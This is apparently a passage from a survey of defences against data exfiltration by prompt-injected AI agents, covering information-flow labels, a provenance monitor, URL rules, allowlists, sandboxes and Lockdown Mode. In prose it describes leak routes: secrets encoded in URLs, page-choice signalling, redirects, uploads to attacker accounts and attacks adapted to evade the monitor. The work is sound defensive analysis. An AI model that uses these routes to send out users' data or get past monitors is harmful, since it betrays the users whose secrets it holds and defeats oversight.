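| Ordinary agent with label checks | 42% | 44% |
| FIDES with label checks | 50% | 61% |

With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES with its checks turned off. None succeeded against either agent with the checks on. AgentDojo counted three successes against FIDES, but the researchers examined them and concluded they weren't real. The label checks thus provided the security, and hiding data in variables recovered some of the lost tasks. But in the travel environment, FIDES completed fewer tasks than the ordinary agent with checks (41% versus 73% with GPT-4o), partly because the model used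 the variables incorrectly.

The perfect security result depends on every untrusted field being labelled correctly. The researchers marked a data field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so no attack could arrive through a mislabelled field. They also hid only untrusted data, not confidential data, and didn't use restricted answer types. The results are good evidence about injected instructions, but they don't show how well an agent can work with confidential data it needs for its task.

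### A monitor that follows files

Hossain and colleagues also built a monitor that can supply the facts for the most informative approval prompt in their study, described above. It records the agent's actual tool calls and links every new file to the data it came from. In their invoice example, it links report.csv to the raw invoice rows. Before the agent sends the file, the monitor compares those links with the user's instruction to share only totals, and classifies the action as allowed, a violation or unknown.

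In a test at 120 points where an agent was about to violate the user's instructions, the monitor detected 107 of the violations (89.2%), missed seven and classified six as unknown. At 120 harmless points, it raised five false alarms and classified two as unknown.

The researchers then used the monitor as a gate that blocked both violations and unknowns. Each figure below is out of 120 runs:

| Agent | Unsafe actions executed, gate off | Gate on | Harmless tasks completed, gate off | Gate on |
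|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3.1-8B | 52 (43.3%) | 6 (5.0%) | 104 | 100 |
| Qwen3-8B | 58 (48.3%) | 7 (5.8%) | 110 | 106 |

They also removed parts of the monitor to find out which ones mattered. This table covers the 80 violations that depended on earlier steps:

| Version of the monitor | Violations detected | False alarms at 120 harmless points |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 69 of 80 | 5 |
| No links between files and their sources | 48 of 80 | 6 |
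| No record of the combined effect of earlier steps | 16 of 80 | 3 |
| No comparison with the user's instructions | 30 of 80 | 15 |
| Some tool activity missing from the record | 51 of 80 | 8 |

The last row matters for real products because some of their tools may not report everything they do. With an incomplete record, the gate also reduced the share of harmless tasks completed to 76.7%. Attacks adapted to the monitor lowered detection to 60 of 80.

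The monitor takes a median of 24 milliseconds per check and needs no extra calls to an AI model. But the 120 violations were five scripted variants of each of 24 scenarios, so they provide less evidence than 120 independent attacks would. Counting unknowns, the gate would have stopped 7 of the 120 harmless actions, or 5.8%. At that rate, an agent that took 100 such actions a day would have about six blocked by mistake.

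### When labels spread to everything

Once a model has read a secret, the software can't reliably determine which of the model's later words depend on it, so the safe assumption is that all of them do. Under that assumption, the agent in the running example could no longer fetch any outside page, even a weather forecast, after reading the configuration file. Researchers who study information flow call this problem label creep.

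Untrusted data spreads in the same way. In the FIDES tests with GPT-4o, label checks reduced the ordinary agent's success rate on Slack tasks from 93% to 20%, because reading one untrusted message restricted everything that followed. FIDES raised the rate to 48% by keeping such messages in variables.

Costa and colleagues mention another remedy, which is to identify the messages that influenced a response and regenerate it from those alone, so that it inherits fewer labels. Microsoft is considering labels that apply to single messages or expire when the agent condenses its history. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) uses an AI model to compare outgoing text with the labelled records the agent has read. This could let harmless text through, but it brings back the errors that AI reviewers make.

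Narrower tracking can also miss data it should follow. Cai and Wen (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, point out that private data can reappear in different words, influence a decision or return in a later session through the agent's memory. In a benchmark of 400 scenarios, their tracker found substantially more of these flows than a FIDES-style system did. A label on the whole conversation would cover rewording, but it would help with memory only if the software saved the label with the data.

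### Who writes the policies and handles exceptions

CaMeL's designers acknowledge that people have to write and update security policies. Tallam and Miller expect this to become difficult in organisations with hundreds of tools, where rules may be duplicated or inconsistent, and recommend a central library of reusable rules. Microsoft proposes deriving basic policies from the descriptions developers already attach to their tools, such as whether a tool only reads data and whether it contacts outside systems.

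Labelling mistakes can remove the protection without warning. Agent Framework treats data from a tool without labels as trusted and public. If the developer in the running example forgot to label the file-reading tool, the framework would treat the key as public and allow the fetch. Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled data should count as untrusted instead.

Strict policies also send some decisions back to a person. CaMeL can ask the user about an unfamiliar recipient, and Agent Framework can turn a blocked call into an approval prompt. A user who clicks Allow releases the key despite the labels. CaMeL's designers recognise the risk of user fatigue.

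Microsoft replies that the software needs fewer approvals from users and can explain each request by showing where the data came from and who would newly receive it. A similar prompt worked best in Hossain and colleagues' study, but volunteers who saw it still approved 24% of harmful requests. Agent Framework's current prompt is less informative. It names the tool and the label that caused the block but doesn't show the full set of labels.

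### Leaks that labels can miss

A strict version of the label rule would stop the page-choice method described earlier. If the model has read the key, every URL it writes inherits the key's label, even the address of an ordinary article. But an observer may still learn something from which tools the agent uses, how often it uses them and in what order. Tallam and Miller give the example of a program that repeats a harmless request a secret number of times. Anyone with the access logs can count the requests. They suggest capping such loops or combining the requests into one.

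Costa and colleagues accept that FIDES doesn't stop this kind of leak. To stop it, FIDES would have to block almost every call with a publicly visible effect after the agent had read anything confidential, which they consider too restrictive. Restricted answers can also leak data. At one bit each, 128 yes/no answers could carry a 128-bit key, so a policy that accepts such answers should limit their total number.

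Errors in the tracking software can also let data leak. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL labels a variable when a secret condition causes the program to change it, but not when the condition causes the program to leave it alone, even though the unchanged value can reveal just as much. CaMeL also discards its labels when it retries a failed program, so repeated attempts could reveal a secret one bit at a time. In response, Garby and colleagues wrote an interpreter with computer-checked proofs that it handles labels correctly, although their guarantee still allows a small leak through whether a program finishes.

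Labels can also disappear when one agent gives instructions to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL but without policies, and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants from a database that contained an injected instruction. The coordinating agent copied text derived from the database into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the whole request as its user's words and also emailed the summary to an outside address. The researchers' solution sends instructions and data separately and keeps the labels attached to the data. It stopped every attack in their tests but reduced the success rate on AssetOpsBench by a further 3.2 points on average.

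### Use in products

Microsoft has released this kind of tracking, but only as an experimental option. FIDES became available in Agent Framework in May 2026, and developers have to turn it on. Microsoft and GitHub later added it to GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent, where users enable it through a setting. So far, it enforces policies there only for selected tools from GitHub's MCP server.

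GitHub's server can now label data from private repositories as private and issues in public repositories as untrusted. With those labels, Copilot CLI can block the GitHub leak that Willison described by stopping an agent that has read both kinds of data from posting to a public page. The labels are sent in a general-purpose metadata field of the Model Context Protocol. Microsoft plans to work with the protocol's developers to standardize the labels, and has published a gateway that adds them to data from servers that don't.

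## Deployed checks on where data is sent

Many products check where data is going, though most don't track where it came from. The simplest check is a domain allowlist, which lets an agent contact listed websites and either blocks requests to other sites or refers them to a person. The check ignores the text of the request, so encoding the data doesn't help an attacker. In the running example, an allowlist would stop the fetch unless someone had added reports.example, which a regular reader of the site might well have done.

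Lan and colleagues tested an allowlist only against a domain that wasn't on it, but real attackers can look for ways to send data out through allowed sites.

### Redirects and shared services

If software checks only the first domain in a link, a redirect can take the request from a trusted site to an attacker's server. OpenAI gives this as one reason for not relying on lists of trusted sites. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* describes an open redirect on Anthropic's own claude.com, which means a link to that site can forward visitors to an address an attacker chooses.

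An agent's software can close this gap by checking each new address before it follows a redirect. This check would not have stopped SearchLeak, because Bing's own server fetched the attacker's address and the user's browser contacted only Bing.

Checking an address against a list of trusted sites can also go wrong. Before version 1.0.111, Claude Code checked only whether an address began with the name of a trusted site, such as modelcontextprotocol.io. According to Sonatype's *CVE-2026-24052*, an attacker could register a domain like modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com, and Claude Code could contact it without the user's consent. The owner of example.com controls that address, even though it begins with the trusted name. Many people in Albakry and colleagues' survey made the same mistake when reading URLs.

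Better matching doesn't help if outsiders can read what people send to a permitted site. In November 2025, Willison noted that the default allowlist for the browser tool in Antigravity, Google's code editor, included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and read the requests that arrive there. Most users would lose little if that entry were removed. Blocking github.com is harder because programmers rely on it heavily, but Docker, whose software isolates programs from the rest of a computer, warns that agents could leak data through content that users post there.

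OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a preset allowlist called "Common dependencies" for tasks that run on OpenAI's servers. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* lists about 70 entries in the preset, including github.com, google.com and azure.com. In May 2026, PromptArmor's *Configuring Codex securely across every platform and use case* reported that the preset still allowed leaks that researchers had already demonstrated.

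Sometimes the risky service belongs to the vendor. In October 2025, Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* showed that Claude's tool for running code could contact Anthropic's API under its default settings, and that an injected instruction could make it upload the user's files to the attacker's account. One upload could hold 30 megabytes, compared with about 1,500 bytes for the 2,000-character URL discussed earlier. Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, then confirmed five days later that such reports were in scope. The Claude Cowork leak of January 2026 and Oasis Security's attack that March involved the same service.

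An allowlist couldn't catch these uploads because they went to the correct domain but the wrong account. Embrace The Red proposed letting the tool communicate only with the logged-in user's account, which would stop these uploads without blocking the service.

### OpenAI's rule for public URLs

In January 2026, OpenAI published a rule for ChatGPT based on the exact URL instead of the domain. OpenAI uses a crawler that finds public web pages, as a search engine does, and records their URLs without access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. Any URL it has recorded exists independently of any conversation, so it is unlikely to contain the current user's secrets.

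Before an agent loads a page or image automatically, the software checks whether the exact URL is in the crawler's index. If it is, the agent can load it without asking the user. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning before opening the link.

In the running example, the crawler may well have recorded `https://reports.example/summary`, so the agent could read the page. It would not have recorded the version ending in the encoded key, because nobody has published that address, so the fetch would not run automatically. An address containing the key in hexadecimal or encrypted form would also be missing from the index.

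Under this rule, a site's owner doesn't have to be trustworthy. An attacker's page may be in the index, but its fixed address can't contain data from a later conversation. A github.com address with a key in it would fail the check, although many programmers' allowlists would let it through. Redirects also matter less, because a URL without private data has none to pass on.

Harmless URLs can fail the check too, such as the address of a page published a few minutes ago or a personal link for tracking a parcel. URLs that the user enters seem to be exempt. Johann Rehberger, the security researcher who writes Embrace The Red, believes ChatGPT treats them as safe for the rest of the chat.

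Anthropic has a similar rule, but it checks URLs against the conversation instead of a public index. According to Anthropic's early 2026 documentation, *Web fetch tool*, Claude can't fetch a URL it composed itself. It can fetch URLs from the user's messages, the results of the developer's own tools, and earlier searches and fetches. The agent in the running example composed the URL containing the key, so the tool would refuse to fetch it.

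This rule needs no crawler, but strangers can supply some of the permitted addresses. Willison points out that developers often insert untrusted text, such as an email, into what the software treats as a user message. Claude can then fetch any link in that text. Until July 2026, Claude could also fetch links that appeared in pages it had already fetched. Anthropic then closed this gap, which Ayush Paul had found in the Claude app.

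| URL | Domain allowlist | OpenAI's rule | Anthropic's rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| The example URL with the key | Allowed if reports.example is listed | Not loaded automatically | Blocked |
| A public article found by web search | Allowed if the site is listed | Allowed if the crawler has recorded it | Allowed |
| A private link the user typed | Allowed if the site is listed | Allowed, as Rehberger understands it | Allowed |
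| One of 36 public pages, chosen to signal a character | Allowed if the site is listed | Allowed if the crawler has recorded it | Allowed if the URL came from a permitted source |

### Rehberger's history and remaining objection

Rehberger first reported to OpenAI in early 2023 that ChatGPT could leak data through a URL without the user clicking anything. OpenAI had no programme for rewarding such reports and, by Rehberger's account, showed little interest in fixing the problem. Microsoft's Bing Chat had the same flaw, and Microsoft stopped it from loading most images in May 2023.

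OpenAI added a `url_safe` check that December, but it wasn't clear how the check decided which URLs were safe. Rehberger found ways around it and presented some at the 2024 Black Hat Europe conference. The macOS and iOS apps lacked the check in places. Around August 2025, OpenAI strengthened the check enough to stop the attacks Rehberger had published, though ZombieAgent still worked until December. OpenAI's paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents* describes the current version.

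Rehberger considers the new rule a significant improvement but not a complete solution. An agent can still spell out a secret by choosing which public pages to visit, a method that Embrace The Red described in 2023 and that OpenAI's paper also acknowledges. Storing a copy of each page and banning repeat visits would make this harder, but Rehberger had not tested whether ChatGPT already used either measure.

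Rehberger also worries that developers at OpenAI may not know about the check when they build new features. The gaps in the macOS and iOS apps show that a good check in one part of a product doesn't protect the others.

Neither OpenAI's announcement nor Rehberger's account of the paper gives any measurements of how well the rule works. OpenAI promises only to prevent quiet leaks through the URL itself, not that a page in the index is trustworthy or free of injected instructions.

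### Safe Url and the warning to the user

In March 2026, OpenAI described Safe Url, a protection designed to detect when a request would send a third party something the assistant learned in the conversation. When it detects such a request, ChatGPT either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to try another way. OpenAI argues that detecting a malicious instruction can be as hard as detecting a lie, so a product should also limit what a deceived agent can do. Safe Url covers page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research, the mode that ShadowLeak exploited.

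The March announcement refers readers to the January one for details, so Safe Url and the public-URL rule are probably parts of the same system. But the announcements differ on what the user sees. January's sample dialog shows only the raw URL and a general warning, while the March announcement describes showing the information itself. To do that, the software would have to find the private data in the URL and, in the running example, decode it. Neither announcement explains how.

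Blocking the request is safer than showing a warning, because the result doesn't depend on the user. With a warning like January's, the user would see the name of a site they had asked about, followed by an unreadable code. The same warning would appear for a harmless parcel-tracking link. In 2024, *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* suggested asking users to confirm every link, but only as a temporary solution.

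OpenAI rejected strict allowlists partly because frequent false alarms can train people to click through warnings. Its own rule could cause the same problem. Suppose that 2% of an agent's fetches use URLs missing from the index and that one fetch in 10,000 is a leak:

```
fetches missing from the index    10,000 × 0.02  =  200
leaks among them                                      1
harmless fetches stopped          200 − 1        =  199
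```

If every one of these fetches produced a warning, the user would see 199 false alarms for each leak. The 2% is invented for illustration. OpenAI's announcements don't give the real figure or the share of cases in which the agent tries another site instead.

### Email, shared documents and internal services

A public index can't help with an email, because a new private message is not in any index. The same is true of an edit to a shared document, a comment on a bug report or a request to a company's internal API. For these tools, the software has to check which people or accounts will receive the data.

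For instance, an email tool could send messages only to the user's colleagues or people already in the conversation. A similar limit would have blocked the WhatsApp message to the attacker's number. It would not have helped in Hossain and colleagues' invoice example, where the auditor was an approved recipient and only the attachment was wrong.

Vendors' documentation contains little about limits of this kind. The closest is the advice in OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* for administrators who choose which connected apps people can use in ChatGPT's most restrictive setting. OpenAI grades the apps' actions largely by who could see the result:

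| Action | Risk according to OpenAI |
|---|---|
| Reading or writing in an untrusted app | High |
| Writing in a trusted app where an attacker might see the result | High |
| Writing in a trusted app where only trusted people can see the result | Medium |
| Reading from a trusted app | Medium, but lower than writing |
| Reading from an index managed by the administrator | Medium |

By this standard, posting a comment on a public GitHub issue is high risk, while editing a document that only a trusted team can open is medium risk. The administrator has to work out who can see the result, which is not always obvious. Copilot Cowork's messages went only to the user, but loading the images in them still sent requests to the researchers' server. OpenAI's advice also applies to whole types of action, so it doesn't replace checking the recipient in each call.

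According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex can ask for approval when a tool's developer has labeled it as having side effects, and always asks when the developer has labeled the action destructive. Sending an email doesn't destroy anything, so the stricter rule may not apply to an email that leaks data.

### Sandboxes with restricted networks

A network sandbox can stop a program from contacting an unapproved server even if the command that started the program looked harmless. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes an optional sandbox for shell commands in Claude Code. All network traffic from those commands goes through a proxy, a separate program that permits or refuses each connection. The proxy initially allows no domains, and Claude Code asks the user about each new one. An organisation can configure the sandbox to block unlisted domains without asking.

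Anthropic's proxy decides by host name and doesn't decrypt traffic, so it can't read the query string of an encrypted request. Suppose the agent in the running example made its request from the shell, with the sandbox set to run commands automatically. Claude Code would prompt the user only about whether to allow reports.example, and a user who wanted a summary from that site would have an obvious reason to agree. An organisation can inspect the full request by installing its own proxy to decrypt the traffic.

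The sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start. Claude Code's fetch tool and MCP tools follow permission rules instead. By default, sandboxed commands can read most files on the computer, including those in common locations for cloud credentials and login keys. If the sandbox can't start because a component is missing, Claude Code shows a warning and runs the commands without it, unless the user or an administrator has changed this default.

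Codex gives shell commands no network access by default. Its web search normally reads an index that OpenAI maintains, not live pages. For tasks on OpenAI's servers, Codex lets a setup phase use the internet and the project's configured secrets, then removes those secrets before the agent starts work. Even if an injected instruction later got the agent to send data out, those secrets would no longer be available to it.

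These protections depend on the user's settings. If someone turns on network access on their own computer, commands can contact any server unless they also turn on a separate proxy that applies domain rules. For tasks on OpenAI's servers, users can restrict the agent to request types that normally only retrieve data, such as GET. This blocks many uploads but not the one in the running example, because an ordinary page fetch is a GET request and its URL can contain the key.

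### Switching off live connections

ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode removes many of the routes for sending data out. OpenAI announced it for organisations in February 2026, in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, and extended it to personal accounts in June. In this mode, ChatGPT browses only stored copies of web pages, so no live requests leave OpenAI's network. Deep Research and Agent Mode are unavailable. Users also can't approve network access for code that ChatGPT writes in its Canvas editor, so a hurried approval can't release data that way.

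In the running example, Lockdown Mode would let the agent read a stored copy of the report but stop it from sending reports.example the URL containing the key. It should also prevent leaks through the choice of page, because the site's owner can't see which stored pages the agent opens. Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode because it limits how data can leave instead of trying to recognise every injected instruction.

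The mode causes stale or missing search results and removes several major features. OpenAI doesn't consider it necessary for most users, and people with personal accounts can turn it off for a single chat. It doesn't affect network access in Codex or automatically disable every connected app in workspaces that an organisation manages. OpenAI warns that data could still leak through enabled apps, unforeseen combinations of features or new methods.

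### Which coding agents asked in 2025

Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Takedown*, examined eight widely used coding agents and gave them code names because vendors were still dealing with the reported flaws. Four had a built-in tool for fetching web pages:

| Agent | Did its fetch tool need approval? |
|---|---|
| A1 | Yes, always |
| A4 | No |
| A5 | The researchers reported no missing approval |
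| A7 | The researchers reported no missing approval |

An injected instruction could therefore make A4 send out anything the model had read, which by default included the user's open files. A4 could also read files outside the project without approval, so the leak could include files from elsewhere on the computer.

An approval prompt on the fetch tool didn't block every way of sending data out. A7 ran shell commands without approval by default, and a shell command can also fetch a page. A2 had no fetch tool, but its diagram viewer could send data out by loading an image. In A1, add-ons set whether their own tools needed approval. Of the ten most-installed VS Code extensions that offered tools to agents, seven didn't require it, including a web search extension from Microsoft. In four of the eight agents, Lee and colleagues found ways to steal files from anywhere on the computer without any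 approval.

The audit describes products as they were in 2025. It recorded A4's missing prompt as reported but not fixed, and because A4 is a code name, readers can't check whether that has changed. Zed added a confirmation to its fetch tool in August 2025. Since then, AI reviewers have replaced some prompts in Claude Code and Codex. A new audit would have to test both whether a prompt appears and which calls those reviewers let through.

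### Rates that vendors don't publish

OpenAI and Anthropic have published error rates for their AI reviewers, but their documentation for allowlists, URL rules, sandboxes and Lockdown Mode gives no rates of leaks, blocks or false alarms. OpenAI also doesn't report how often the ShadowLeak email works with Safe Url in place.

OpenAI could measure some of this from ordinary use by counting how many URLs are missing from the index, how often the agent finds another page and how often users open a link despite the warning. Measuring missed leaks would require planted test data. Results would need to be separated for URLs, page choices, messages and uploads to permitted services, because a low average miss rate could hide a route where leaks are almost always missed.
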